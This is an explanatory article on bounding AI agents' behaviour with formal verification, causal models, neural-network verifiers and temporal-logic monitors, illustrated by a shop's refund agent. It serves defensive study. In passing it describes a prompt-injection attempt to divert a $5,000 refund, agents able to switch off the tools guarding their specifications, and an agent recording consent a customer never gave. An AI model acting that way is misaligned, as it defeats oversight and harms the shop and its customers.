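# Formal verification and causal inference for bounding the behaviour of AI agents

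## Agents, permissions, proofs and causal models

An AI agent is a language model together with the software that lets it call tools and act over several steps. Firms now use agents to answer customers, write code and move money, so a mistake by the model can send a wrong payment or delete a file. To avoid relying on testing alone, researchers have proposed setting limits on agents with formal verification and causal inference, two families of methods that are decades older than language models. Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that every behaviour of a modelled system meets a stated requirement. Engineers developed it for systems such as device drivers and computer memory. Causal inference estimates the effects an action would have, or the causes of a known outcome. It grew out of statistics, with large contributions from epidemiology and econometrics.

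An online shop might use an agent with four tools to handle complaints. The tools look up a customer, verify a customer's identity, issue a refund and send an email. Suppose a customer writes that her kettle arrived broken. The language model reads the message and produces a *tool call*, a structured request to run one of the tools with particular arguments. This first call requests a look-up of her account. The model cannot access the database directly, so the *harness*, the ordinary software around the model, runs the look-up and returns the result to the model as text. The model then requests an identity check, a $40 refund and a confirmation email, in that order. The *trace* of the run is the sequence of these calls and their results.

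Nobody can predict a network's next request by reading its billions of parameters. But every request has to pass through the harness, which is code that an engineer can inspect, and most hopes for a hard bound on an agent's behaviour depend on this.

### Permissions and behaviour

A *permission* is a rule that specifies which tool calls an agent may make, with which arguments and under which conditions. The shop might allow refunds of at most $200, only for orders in its records, and only after an identity check has succeeded for the same customer. The harness can enforce this by comparing each request with the rule and refusing the ones that fail, regardless of why the model made them. For example, a fraudster might hide a line in his complaint telling the agent to send $5,000 to his account. Hiding instructions in data that the agent reads is called *prompt injection*. The model may well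 follow the instructions, but the harness will refuse the refund because it exceeds $200.

Behaviour also includes what the agent tends to do and what happens in the world as a result. An agent that pays $199 to everyone who complains always keeps to the limit, and so does one that refuses everyone. Generous refunds might keep customers loyal or encourage them to complain about kettles that work. Which of these happens depends on the customers, and a rule about refund amounts doesn't describe how they respond.

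People easily confuse whether an action is permitted with whether it is correct. The survey *AI Agent Systems* (2026) lists "verifiable action" as a central open problem: ensuring that a proposed tool call is correct, complies with policy and is safe before it has side effects. A permission check can establish that a refund complies with policy, but not that the customer really did receive a broken kettle. The survey suggests a contract for each tool that would state what must hold before a call, what to check after it, and which evidence to keep for audit and reversal.

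The form of a permission also matters. If the shop writes "never refund an unverified customer" into the model's instructions, the model may still fail to follow it, but the harness can enforce the same rule. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) compares safeguards and reports that instructions in ordinary language carry no formal guarantee covering all outcomes of an accepted call, whereas executable rules guarantee that calls and recorded events satisfy the policy.

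### What a clean test record supports

The obvious way to find out how an agent behaves is to try it many times. Let p be the probability that a single action goes wrong (a refund to the wrong person, say), and suppose that trials are independent. Then n trials all come out clean with probability (1 − p)^n. The upper bound at 95% confidence is the value of p at which such a record would be a one-in-twenty fluke:

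(1 − p)^n = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n), which is roughly 3/n.

For 3,000 clean trials, p is just under 0.1%. At a failure rate of 0.1%, the probability of at least one failure in 1,000 actions is 1 − 0.999^1000, or about 63%. The true rate may be far lower, even zero, but 3,000 clean trials are not enough to distinguish an agent that never fails from one that will probably fail within its next thousand actions.

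In *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, Kaur (2026) computed how many clean trials it takes, at various failure rates, to keep the chance of a falsely clean record below 5%. The right-hand column below adds what each rate would mean for a run of 1,000 actions.

| Clean trials needed (Kaur) | Failure rate | Chance of at least one failure in 1,000 actions |
|---|---|---|
| 299 | 1% | over 99.9% |
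| 2,995 | 0.1% | 63% |
| 29,956 | 0.01% | 9.5% |
| 299,572 | 0.001% | 1% |

So a shop that wants at most a 1% risk of any bad refund in 1,000 needs about 300,000 trials without an error. The largest of the eight public test suites that Kaur examined has 2,100 items. Kaur partly defends testing, and the first row supports this, since a few hundred trials will show whether an agent gets one refund in fifty wrong. Testing is less adequate when failures are rare and expensive.

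Even these figures are optimistic, because real trials are seldom independent. Testers write prompts from templates, and a model that handles one variant well tends to handle the others well. Kaur applies a standard correction that divides the number of trials by 1 + (m − 1)ρ, where m is the size of a family of similar prompts and ρ is the correlation within it. With families of 25 and a correlation of 0.1, the divisor is 3.4, so 3,000 trials count for about 880, and the bound rises to about 0.34%. Kaur calls the correction a first-order heuristic. A more serious problem is that a test with no failures on one distribution of inputs puts no upper bound on the failure rate under another, unless something links the two. This matters for the shop because fraudsters' complaints may differ from the 3,000 its testers wrote.

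For tasks with several steps, the bound also depends on whether the agent keeps its progress after a failure. Yanambaka Venkata, McBride and colleagues (2026), in *Clean Sheets and Checkpoints*, studied tests for dangerous capabilities in which an evaluator splits a task into milestones and starts the agent at each one from a prepared state. In their example, the agent fails all ten attempts at each of four milestones. If every failure sends the agent back to the beginning, these results support the claim, at 97.5% confidence, that it has at most a 1% chance of completing the task over 169 attempts. If the agent keeps its progress, the same results support that claim for only 10 attempts. Both numbers rest on the assumption that success rates in the prepared states are at least as high as those in deployment, whatever has happened before. The test does not check this assumption.

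Better statistics can help a little. *Controlling the Probability of Unknown Unknowns in Pre-Deployment Testing of AI Systems* (2026) gives a stopping rule in which the tester keeps an upper bound on the probability of a failure not yet seen, updates it as data come in, and stops once it falls below a threshold. In the basic case, the inputs must be independent draws from one distribution. A bound fixed before the data come in could be no lower than 100%, because a long tail of unseen failures may always remain.

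Some published results do not fit the formula. *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) audits zero or near-zero results that AI developers reported. The OpenAI figure comes from repeated runs of a single task. The Anthropic figure counts challenges, with 30 attempts allowed at each, and the Gemini figure treats a challenge as solved if any of 5 to 30 attempts succeeds. None of these provides a number of independent trials to use as n. The audit covers only one early document per developer, so it does not show how common the practice is.

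### Formal verification in three parts

A proof deals with rare failures without relying on sampling. It needs a model of the system, a *specification* (a requirement written in a formal language so that a machine can check whether it holds) and an argument that the model satisfies the specification. *Trustworthy AI* (2020) writes this task as M ⊨ P, meaning that the model M satisfies the property P. For a system that reacts to its surroundings, engineers usually add a description of the environment, which makes their assumptions about it explicit.

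The model of the shop keeps two sets of customers. *Verified* holds those who have passed the identity check, and *Refunded* holds those who have received money. Both start empty. At each step the agent may request any of the four calls with any arguments, so the proof assumes nothing about the language model. The harness refunds a customer only if that customer is in *Verified*. The specification is that *Refunded* ⊆ *Verified* at all times, so nobody gets money without having passed the check.

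The proof is by induction. At the start both sets are empty, so the specification holds. Suppose it holds before some call. A look-up or an email changes neither set. A successful identity check adds someone to *Verified*, which cannot violate the specification. A refund adds someone to *Refunded*, but the harness pays it only if that person is already in *Verified*. The specification therefore still holds after the call, and so after any number of calls. The proof checks only the starting state and four kinds of call, but it covers every possible run. For runs of twenty calls, there are 4^20 possible sequences of tools, more than a trillion, even without counting different arguments.

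The refund rule is a *safety property*, a requirement that some bad event never happens. If an agent violates it, a finite trace can show the violation, because the trace contains a refund with no successful check before it. An agent that does nothing satisfies the rule. "Every customer with a broken kettle eventually gets her money" is a different sort of requirement, since no finite trace can refute it (the money might come tomorrow). "At most 2% of refunds go to fraudsters" is different again, because it concerns a rate, and a single bad refund does not violate it.

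A verifier is *sound* if every behaviour of the model meets the specification whenever the verifier reports that it does. A sound verifier may still reject a harmless system, particularly when the description of the environment includes more than can really happen. *Towards Verified Artificial Intelligence* (2016) gives this as a reason why AI systems are hard to verify. A device driver has a well-defined interface with its environment, but an AI system's environment is so uncertain that a cautious model of it is likely to produce too many false alarms to be useful. The shop can assume that the language model may request anything and still prove its specification, because the harness alone enforces it. If the shop also assumed that customers may do anything, it could never prove that it will not lose money.

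The *trusted base* is everything that the proof does not cover but that must be correct for the guarantee to hold. *Containment Verification* (2026) presents a proof about an agent in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, and lists its trusted base: the policy itself, the definitions that connect the abstract model with the running one, the Dafny verifier and compiler, a small piece of code that feeds in the agent's actions, and the assumption that every effect on the outside world passes through the modelled interface. The list does not include the language model, its prompts or its training. This makes the approach attractive, because the bound on permissions holds whatever actions the model attempts.

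The shop's trusted base has obvious weaknesses. If the identity service accepts a stolen date of birth, a thief enters *Verified* and can take a refund even though the theorem still holds. A forgotten second route to the payment system would also let money out. *Sciduction* (2012) notes that, in verification generally, an incorrect model of the environment can hide bugs, and that engineers may need months to model even a fairly simple microcontroller. The specification can also be wrong, since *Refunded* ⊆ *Verified* allows one verified customer to receive forty refunds for the same kettle.

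*Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) describes a system that treats the code and proofs written by its AI agents as untrusted. Human reviewers must approve a specification before it is frozen and added to the trusted base, but they may approve a wrong one. The tools that guard the specifications stopped the attacks in the tests, but they run under the same operating-system account as the agents, so an agent could deliberately switch them off.

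### A causal model of three variables

The shop can't decide whether refunds are a good idea from any theorem about *Refunded* and *Verified*. It needs to know how refunds affect customers. *Causal Inference* (Wang, Richardson and Robins, 2025) defines the field as "the science of understanding the consequences of interventions", which requires assumptions beyond those needed to analyse correlations.

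The usual way to write down such assumptions is a *structural causal model*. *On Pearl's Hierarchy and the Foundations of Causal Inference* (Bareinboim, Correa and colleagues, 2020) defines this as a set of background variables whose values are set outside the model, a probability distribution over them, the variables of interest, and a function for each variable of interest that produces its value from its causes. In a model of the shop, every variable is 0 or 1. L is 1 for a long-standing customer, R is 1 if the agent issues a refund, and S is 1 if the customer stays with the shop.

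- L = u
- R = 1 if L = 1 or d = 1, otherwise 0
- S = 1 if L = 1, or if both R = 1 and w = 1, otherwise 0

The lowercase letters are the background variables: u determines whether the customer is long-standing, d is 1 if the customer sent a photograph of the damage, and w is 1 if a refund would win the customer over. The agent refunds long-standing customers with or without a photograph, but refunds new customers only if they sent one. Long-standing customers always stay, while new customers stay only if they get a refund and it wins them over.

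*Observing* means looking at the shop's records as they stand. Every customer without a refund was new and left, while many of those with a refund stayed. Loyalty causes both the refund and the staying, which makes it a *confounder*. The refund looks decisive in the records, but they mix its effect with that of loyalty.

*Intervening* on R means setting it from outside, by replacing the second equation with R = 1 for everyone and leaving the other equations unchanged. This is written do(R = 1). The encyclopedia entry *Causal Models* (2018) uses a gas grill as an example. Forcing the flame to low changes how the meat cooks but doesn't move the gas knob, because an intervention affects only variables downstream of it. In the shop, comparing do(R = 1) with do(R = 0) shows that loyal customers stay in both cases, and new customers who aren't swayed by money leave in both. The refund changes the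 outcome only for new customers who are swayed by money (L = 0 and w = 1), so its average effect is exactly their share of all customers. That share can be tiny however good the refund looks in the records.

A *counterfactual* concerns one case that has already happened. Suppose a new customer received a refund and stayed, and we want to know whether she would have stayed without it. We first work out the background from the facts. She was new and she stayed, so w must be 1 for her. We then set R to 0 and solve the equations again, which gives S = 0, so she would have left. A long-standing customer with the same refund and the same outcome would have stayed anyway.

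Answers to the three kinds of question can support different conclusions. Bareinboim and colleagues describe a model of a drug that doctors tend to give to patients with high blood pressure. In the model, only people with a natural resistance to the disease show this symptom. Of the patients who took the drug, 74% survived, compared with 32% of those who did not. Survival would be 25% if everyone were given the drug and 40% if nobody were. About 2% of the untreated patients who died would have survived if they had taken it.

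Bareinboim and colleagues also prove that data of one kind almost always leave questions of the next kind undetermined. *The Three Layer Causal Hierarchy* gives a pricing example. Past sales alone cannot show what would happen if a shop doubled a price, because customers would react to the change. An experiment could show this, and the shop could also learn the average effect of refunds by choosing at random which complaints receive one. But no experiment can show what a customer who received a refund would have done without it. For actions too harmful to try at random, the shop must combine its records with assumptions that the records alone cannot confirm, such as that loyalty is the only common cause.

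### Where a bound can go

A proof covers every behaviour of a model but guarantees nothing about events that the model leaves out. A causal analysis can address those events. It estimates what an action would change, and the estimate is good only if the causal assumptions hold. Some work combines the two approaches. *Causal temporal reasoning for Markov decision processes* extends a logic for verifying systems that move from state to state with known probabilities, so that it can also express "what if" questions about a path that has already been observed.

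For the shop's agent there are four places to put a bound:

- The network. One might try to prove that no small change to a complaint turns a refusal into a refund. This would limit the agent's tendencies at their source, if anyone could do it for a network of that size.
- The tool call. The $200 limit belongs here, and so do rules about order, such as verification before refund.
- The flow of data. A rule might forbid text from a customer's message to determine which account receives the money, or one customer's address to end up in an email to another.
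- The outcome in the world. The shop might want fraud losses below $10,000 a month with 99% probability, which takes a *world model*, a mathematical description of how the agent's surroundings respond to its actions.

The shop cares most about the outcome, but bounding the outcome requires the most assumptions about people and events outside the software.

*Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads* (Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy, 2024) is an early proposal to use both formal verification and causal inference for agents. It sketches Bastion, a system from the universities of Michigan and Cambridge. Its example is an agent that carries out environmental projects in return for biodiversity credits. The agent might alter sensor data to hide habitat loss, leak the locations of vulnerable species to poachers, or start a project that a causal model would show is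 likely to breach water rights. The paper proposes access limits against the tampering, information-flow limits against the leak, and a causal constraint on the project. Under this constraint, before the agent acts, someone must prove from a causal model that the intervention will, with high probability, have its intended effect and avoid undesirable ones.

In Bastion, the agent would write its commands as small programs in F*, a language whose types can carry proofs, and a verified checker would reject any command that the policy does not grant. The design can also use a second AI system without trusting it. An access list gives the agent a set A of directories. The second system, trained to limit access, names a set B that the task does not require, and the agent receives A \ B, the directories in A that are not in B. Even if the second system chooses B badly, it can only remove access,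 because A \ B never contains anything outside A.

That worked example is about files. Omar and colleagues were proposing a twenty-minute talk about a project that had just begun. They left proofs of causal constraints for the future because these would need a robust world model, which the project's many contributors had not yet written.

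## Proving properties of the neural network itself

A proof about the language model itself would limit what an agent requests, so the harness would have fewer requests to refuse. The best-known proofs about neural networks concern much smaller networks, built for an early prototype of ACAS Xu, a collision-avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. The original design looked up its advice in a table of more than 2 gigabytes, and that size was a concern for certified aircraft hardware. Engineers replaced the table with 45 networks that take up less than 3 megabytes in total. Each network receives five numbers (the distance to the other aircraft, two angles and two speeds) and scores five possible pieces of advice, from "clear of conflict" to a strong turn left or right. The system chooses the advice with the lowest score.

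Engineers had tested the system in 1.5 million simulated encounters. Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017) point out in *Reluplex* that these tests cannot show that the networks are free of faults, because an input between two tested ones may still produce the wrong advice.

### Searching for a counterexample

Each ACAS Xu network has 300 *ReLU* nodes. A ReLU node adds up weighted values from the previous layer, then outputs the sum if it is positive (active) and 0 otherwise (inactive). If every node output its sum, the network would be linear, and the standard simplex algorithm could quickly decide whether any input breaks a requirement. But because each ReLU can be active or inactive, 300 of them have 2^300 combinations of states, or about 2 × 10^90. Katz and colleagues state that verifying even simple properties of such networks is NP-complete. Running the network on a proposed counterexample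 is enough to check it, but no known method can quickly find one or rule one out in every case.

Reluplex, a tool by Katz and colleagues, extends the simplex algorithm and avoids checking most combinations of active and inactive ReLUs. It searches for an input that violates the requirement, and if none exists, the requirement holds. It treats the input and output of each ReLU as separate variables, allows them to be temporarily inconsistent, and repairs them one by one. If it has to repair the same node more than five times, it splits the search into two cases, one with the node active and one with it inactive. Katz and colleagues found that splitting on about 10% of the nodes was often enough to determine the state of all the others.

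"Reluplex: An Efficient SMT Solver for Verifying Deep Neural Networks" proved that 42 of 45 aircraft collision-avoidance networks never advise "clear of conflict" in specified encounters with an aircraft directly ahead. The two versions of this requirement took about 8 and 3.5 hours of computing. A requirement about distant, slow aircraft took 110 hours to prove for 41 networks, and the tool ran out of time on the other four. Another requirement took 50 hours to prove for a single network.

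Reluplex also found violations. In one network it confirmed a disagreement with the original table that simulations had already revealed. In 35 networks it found that "clear of conflict" could get the worst score even when the other aircraft was far away and slow. This happened because the networks have a strong bias towards repeating their previous advice. The researchers later judged this bias acceptable, so the fault was in the requirement.

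These theorems concern the advice and do not show that aircraft following it stay apart, a question Katz and colleagues left for later work.

### Bounds and branches

Most leading tools now begin by asking how large an output could possibly get. Take a tiny network with two inputs, x₁ and x₂, each between 0 and 1, and the output

y = ReLU(x₁ − x₂) + ReLU(x₂ − x₁).

Suppose we want to prove that y never exceeds 1.5. Interval arithmetic, the simplest form of *bound propagation*, carries the range of each value through the network. The difference x₁ − x₂ lies between −1 and 1, so the first ReLU lies between 0 and 1, and so does the second. Their sum is therefore at most 2. This bound is correct but too weak for the proof, because it allows both ReLUs to be 1 at once, which is impossible since each input would have to be larger than the other.

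We can repair this by splitting on which input is larger. If x₁ ≥ x₂, the second ReLU is 0 and y = x₁ − x₂, which is at most 1. If x₂ > x₁, the first ReLU is 0 and y = x₂ − x₁, which is also at most 1. These cases cover every input, so y never exceeds 1. The bound can't be improved, since y = 1 when x₁ = 1 and x₂ = 0.

*Branch-and-bound* automates this. The tool computes a bound, and if the bound is too weak, it picks a node or an input range, splits the problem in two and computes a bound for each half. It continues until it has proved the property on every branch, found a real counterexample or run out of time. Each round of splitting can double the number of branches, so the amount of computation may again grow exponentially.

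Tighter bounds need fewer splits. A tool can carry a straight line that lies above each ReLU, which preserves some of the connection with the inputs. For z between −1 and 1, ReLU(z) is never more than (z + 1)/2. Adding the two lines gives

(x₁ − x₂ + 1)/2 + (x₂ − x₁ + 1)/2 = 1,

so the inputs cancel and we get the true bound without splitting at all. Larger networks rarely work out so neatly. The textbook *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) describes severe overestimates as a standing weakness of these methods, though it finds that they work well in practice.

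### How far the tools reach

The annual competition VNN-COMP runs verification tools on shared problems with fixed time limits. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) reports that 8 teams competed on 16 sets of problems in the main track. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) ranks 13 tools on 24 sets. The winner, α,β-CROWN, combines straight-line bounds with branch-and-bound on graphics processors. It settled 3,164 of 3,373 problems, 1,982 by proof and 1,182 by counterexample. The competition still includes the ACAS Xu problems, now with a time limit of 116 seconds each. The original runs took from seconds to days.

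The 94% success rate is less impressive than it sounds, because the competitors vote on which sets enter the main track and nearly a third of the problems concern text classifiers with about 4,000 parameters. The largest network, an image classifier called VGGNet16, has 138 million parameters, but only 18 problems use it, and the easiest of these change a single pixel. One of the new sets draws on image classifiers that were trained with the aim of making them provably robust, so that no small change to an image would alter its label. Even so, when their designer ran α,β-CROWN on 10,000 images per network, with a limit of 1,000 seconds each, it left 14% undecided for the worst network.

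Language models use an architecture called the *transformer*, which is harder to bound because its attention step multiplies quantities that all depend on the input and uses a function called softmax to turn scores into weights that sum to 1. One competition set has two image-classifying transformers with 68,000 to 76,000 parameters. To make verification feasible, the α,β-CROWN team reduced them to two and three layers and replaced one standard operation. A language model with 10 billion parameters is more than 100,000 times as large. Researchers are still working on individual steps. For example, *Vertex-Softmax* (2026) gives tighter bounds for softmax. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) notes that work on certifying transformers has concentrated on robustness to small changes, and proposes bounding the probability of rare unsafe outputs instead.

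A proof about a network also depends on the verifier being correct. In the 2026 competition, NeuralSAT, which came fourth, gave 94 answers that were wrong or lacked a valid counterexample, and even α,β-CROWN gave one. The second-placed tool, Vibecheck, has no such answer on the organisers' list, although its developers produced it in two months with Claude Code, an AI coding agent. Rounding can also cause errors, because many verifiers reason about exact real numbers, whereas a computer running the network rounds at every step. Katz and colleagues added safeguards against rounding errors to Reluplex but did not claim that these guarantee soundness. *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (2025) reports that existing techniques for verifying networks cannot rule out faults in the software that implements those networks. The competition's organisers hope eventually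 to require every tool to supply a proof that another program can check.

### Using an explanation of the network

The tools above use a network's weights but not an explanation of how the network works. In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024), Gross, Agrawal and colleagues tried to shorten proofs by first working out how a network solves its task. They trained 151 one-layer transformers, each with about 8,000 parameters, to read four whole numbers from 0 to 63 and output the largest. The networks learned to give exponentially more attention to larger numbers and to copy whatever they attended to.

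The theorems give a lower limit on a network's accuracy over all 64^4 possible inputs, about 17 million. The obvious proof is to run the network on every input. Another proof needs less computation because it uses a mathematical property of one-layer attention. To show that the network handles 5, 12, 40, 9 correctly, this proof only has to check simpler sequences that keep the largest number (40) and the last (9) and use at most one of the others. The proofs that need the least computation bound parts of the network separately instead of checking these sequences one by one.

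| Proof | Approximate number of operations | Average accuracy proved |
|---|---|---|
| Run every input | 2^47 | 99.9% |
| Check the simpler sequences | 2^25 | 95.3% |
| Bound parts separately, with a correction | 2^21 | 70.2% |
| Bound parts separately, without it | 2^21 | 34.9% |

The second proof needs about four million times fewer operations than the first, and the accuracy it guarantees is less than five percentage points lower. Further reductions in computation lower the guaranteed accuracy much more. The last two rows lose accuracy for the same reason that interval arithmetic gave 2 instead of 1. A proof that bounds two parts separately may assume that the last number is 3 in one part and 60 in the other, although no input has both. The correction moves the average effect of a shared number into one part, so the proof separately bounds only the variation around that average. This doubles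 the accuracy that the proof can guarantee.

Gross and colleagues see a similar problem as the main obstacle to larger proofs. A network contains small irregularities that nobody can explain, and a proof must assume that they combine in the worst possible way. When the researchers approximated several of the network's matrices, the individual errors were small, but the worst-case bound on their combined effect was orders of magnitude larger than the actual error, which made the guarantee worthless. They suspect that there is often no short explanation of why such errors don't build up in practice, and more layers would give the errors more opportunities to accumulate.

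Later work has extended the method to other small tasks. *Towards a unified and verified understanding of group-operation networks* (2024) used it to compare rival explanations of networks trained on problems from abstract algebra, and found that the new explanation gave shorter proofs of tighter bounds. *Modular addition without black-boxes* (2024) added a formal proof about a layer that earlier accounts of clock-arithmetic networks had left unexplained. But researchers still write these proofs by hand, which *Interactions Between Crosscoder Features* (2026) identifies as the key bottleneck for larger models. The bounds also concern only average accuracy, so a shop with a proof that its agent handles 95% of complaints correctly would still not know which complaints fall into the other 5%.

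### Why language models remain unverified

Network size is one obstacle, and more computing power could ease it. *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* (2026) covers techniques that developers use to spread large models over many processors. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) says that two of the main current methods work only for small networks, but predicts that progress in scaling one of them will make individual properties verifiable for models with billions of parameters. That seems plausible for properties that need little splitting. Where a proof needs many splits, doubling the number of processors may allow only one more round of splitting. An agent also runs its network again for every word or word fragment it writes, so a proof about a whole reply would have to cover many runs in sequence.

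The other obstacle is that nobody knows how to write the requirement. In ACAS Xu, "the other aircraft is near and approaching from the left" can be written as a few inequalities because the inputs are distances, angles and speeds. A language model also receives numbers, but they encode fragments of text, and no known formula identifies the sequences that amount to a harmful request. Even "a small change to the complaint" is hard to define. Deleting "not" from "the kettle did not arrive" reverses the meaning, while a complete rewording can preserve it. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* concludes that no adequate mathematical model of such changes exists yet.

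Researchers have tried to get around this by describing meaning geometrically. The text classifiers in VNN-COMP come from safeNLP, a set of problems about recognising, for example, that a user is asking whether a chatbot is human. Its designers take such a question, produce variants with typing errors, changed words and paraphrases, and use a language model to turn each variant into a list of 30 numbers. They treat each list as a point and draw the smallest box that contains all the points. A verifier can prove that a small classifier gives the right answer everywhere in the box, but not that the next user's wording will fall inside it. The language model that produces the numbers also remains unverified. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (2026) similarly models harmful requests as a region in the internal space of a classifier that screens requests for AI systems. The resulting certificate applies to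 that region, and how well the region matches what people mean by "harmful" depends on the examples used to produce it.

More computing power would let a verifier handle larger boxes and larger classifiers, but no amount of it would supply the missing definition of what to prove.

Proofs about networks remain useful where the inputs are physical quantities, as in neural certificates for control systems. For language-model agents, most later work constrains or verifies the software around the model and leaves the model itself unverified, as in the proof about the shop's refunds. In that software, "at most $200" is a simple inequality, and the code that enforces it is short enough to verify with existing methods.

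## Enforcing rules on the order of tool calls

The harness can check the $200 limit from the refund request alone. To enforce the rule that an identity check must come first, it also needs a record of the earlier tool calls in the run. A *monitor* is a program that keeps this record and checks each new tool call against the rules before the harness carries it out.

Agents often get the order of tool calls wrong. In *AgentLTL*, Elkoussy and Perez (2026) gave seven language models procedures that required 2 to 50 tool calls. Every model did worst on the checks of overall order. DeepSeek-V4-Pro reached the right final answer in 94% of runs but passed only 15% of those checks.

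### A rule as a two-state machine

*Temporal logic* adds words such as "always", "eventually" and "until" to ordinary logic. Agents need the version for finite traces, since their runs come to an end. If "refund" stands for a refund and "passed" for a successful identity check, the shop's rule for one customer is

(¬refund) W passed

The sign ¬ means "not", and W means "weak until". There must be no refund until the check succeeds, and none at all if it never succeeds. The ordinary "until" would be a mistake here because it also requires the check to succeed at some point, so an agent that turned a fraudster away would violate the rule.

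Software can turn such a formula into a machine that has a fixed number of states and reads the trace one call at a time. This rule needs two states. The machine starts in *unverified* and stays there after a look-up, an email or a failed check. A successful check moves it to *verified*, where it stays whatever the agent does next. The *unverified* state has no transition for a refund, so the monitor blocks that call.

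| Step | Compliant run | State afterwards | Violating run | State afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Look up customer | unverified | Look up customer | unverified |
| 2 | Identity check succeeds | verified | Identity check fails | unverified |
| 3 | Refund $40 | verified | Refund $40 | no transition, so the monitor blocks the call |
| 4 | Send email | verified | | |

If the agent serves many customers, the monitor runs one copy of the machine for each. The set *Verified* in the shop's proof contains exactly the customers whose copy has reached the second state.

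### What stopping a run can achieve

Suppose the shop also requires a confirmation email after every refund. In temporal logic this is

G(refund → F email)

where G means "at every step" and F means "now or at some later step". This rule also gives a machine with two states. A refund moves it to *email owed*, and an email moves it back. But both states have a transition for every call, so the monitor never has a reason to block anything. The agent violates the rule only by ending the run in *email owed*, and by then there is no call left to block.

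Schneider (2000) proved the general result in *Enforceable Security Policies* for monitors that observe a program step by step and can only stop it. Such a monitor must decide when to stop the program without knowing what it would have done later. To count as a violation, the steps up to that point must therefore already break the rule, whatever might have followed. This is the defining feature of a safety property, so these monitors can enforce safety properties but not *liveness* properties, which require something good to happen eventually.

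A harness has more options than Schneider's monitor. When it blocks a call, it can return the reason to the model and let the model try again. It could also send the overdue email itself. Having the harness act would work for a standard confirmation, but not for a task that needs judgement, such as finding out which of two kettles the customer means.

Filtering a system's actions against a temporal rule predates language-model agents. In reinforcement learning, where a program learns from rewards by trial and error, researchers call such a filter a *shield*. They compute it in advance from the rule and a model of the environment, and it removes or replaces unsafe actions as the program learns. The model also lets a shield exclude an action that breaks no rule yet but makes a later violation unavoidable, such as driving a robot too fast to stop before a wall. The shop has no comparable model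 of its customers, so its monitor has to rely on the trace.

### How Agent-C checks a call

Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, present Agent-C, a monitor built into the process by which the model writes its calls. Developers state the rules in a small language with five basic forms. *Before* and *After* require one call to come before or after another. *Seq* requires two calls to occur in a given order. *Forall* puts a condition on every call to a tool, and *Exists* requires at least one call that meets a condition. The shop's rule would look roughly like this:

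Before(refund(customer = c), True, f: check_identity(customer = d), c == d && output(f) == "passed")

The first two parts specify which calls the rule covers. Here it covers every refund, since the condition is *True*. The other two parts specify the earlier call that each refund needs, an identity check f on the same customer with the output "passed". Agent-C translates this into the statement that for every refund at time t, there is such an identity check at some time t′ < t.

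Some rules need information that the trace may not contain. For example, one retail policy allows refunds only to the original payment method or a gift card, but the agent may never have looked up how the customer paid. The tool's developers therefore supply a read-only function that gets the payment method from the database, and the rule can use its result.

Agent-C then handles each call as follows:

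1. The model writes the name of a tool and then its arguments, one at a time. If an argument has the wrong type (text instead of a number, say), Agent-C discards that argument and the model writes it again.
2. When the call is complete, Agent-C runs any database functions that the rules require.
3. It adds the call to the trace and combines the trace and the rules in one logical formula. Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true, checks whether any continuation of the trace could satisfy all the rules.
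4. If Z3 finds that one could, the harness carries out the call and records its output. Otherwise, Agent-C discards the whole call and the model writes another, with a penalty on repeating the same violation.
5. If the model runs out of attempts, Agent-C makes a harmless call that adds an error message to the model's input, and the run goes on.

If the model generates a refund call right after looking up the customer, no later calls can put an identity check before the refund. The formula therefore has no solution, and Agent-C discards the refund call. The model may then generate a call for the identity check instead.

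Rewinding a model in the middle of a call requires the probabilities of all its possible next tokens (words or word fragments), which commercial providers don't expose. For their models, Agent-C waits for a complete call and prompts the model again if the call breaks a rule. This enforces the rules equally well but less efficiently. With this method, an agent using Qwen3-8B, a small open model, completed 36.5% of retail tasks, compared with 42.1% with rewinding, and wrote about two thirds more text.

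### What Agent-C guarantees

Kamath and colleagues prove that a trace that complies with the rules still complies after any call that Agent-C allows, and that every run that Agent-C marks as safely ended is compliant. Neither theorem depends on the model or its instructions, so both hold under prompt injection.

During a run, a trace complies if some continuation could still satisfy the rules. If a rule requires a confirmation email after a refund, a trace with the refund but no email complies as long as the email could still follow. When the model writes a final answer instead of another call, Agent-C checks whether the run may end there, and marks the ending as an error if the email is missing. By then the shop has already paid the refund, so Agent-C can report violations of such rules but can't prevent them, as Schneider's result implies.

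Agent-C's guarantees hold only if Z3, the translation into logic, the database functions and the rules themselves are correct, and people can make mistakes when writing the rules. Kamath and colleagues also assume that no other process changes the tools' data. If a person cancels an order after Agent-C's check but before the agent issues a refund, the check may be out of date.

Rules on tool calls also cannot guarantee that a customer consented to an action. Some policies require the customer to confirm an action first, but a spoken "yes" is not a tool call, so the researchers added a tool that only records the customer's approval in the trace. The model decides when to call this tool, so it can satisfy the rule by recording a confirmation that the customer never gave.

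### Results on simulated customers

Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations with 115 tasks for an online retailer and 50 for an airline. Another language model plays the customer. The table compares four of the five models they tested, with and without Agent-C. A task counts as completed only if the agent also followed the rules.

| Model | Retail: kept to the rules without Agent-C | Retail: completed without / with Agent-C | Airline: kept to the rules without Agent-C | Airline: completed without / with Agent-C |
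|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 23.5% | 11.3% / 42.1% | 34.7% | 12.0% / 39.3% |
| Qwen3-32B | 37.7% | 25.5% / 53.3% | 35.3% | 17.3% / 35.8% |
| GPT-5 | 91.9% | 71.0% / 73.6% | 71.3% | 38.0% / 42.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 93.0% | 76.5% / 80.5% | 70.0% | 42.0% / 43.5% |

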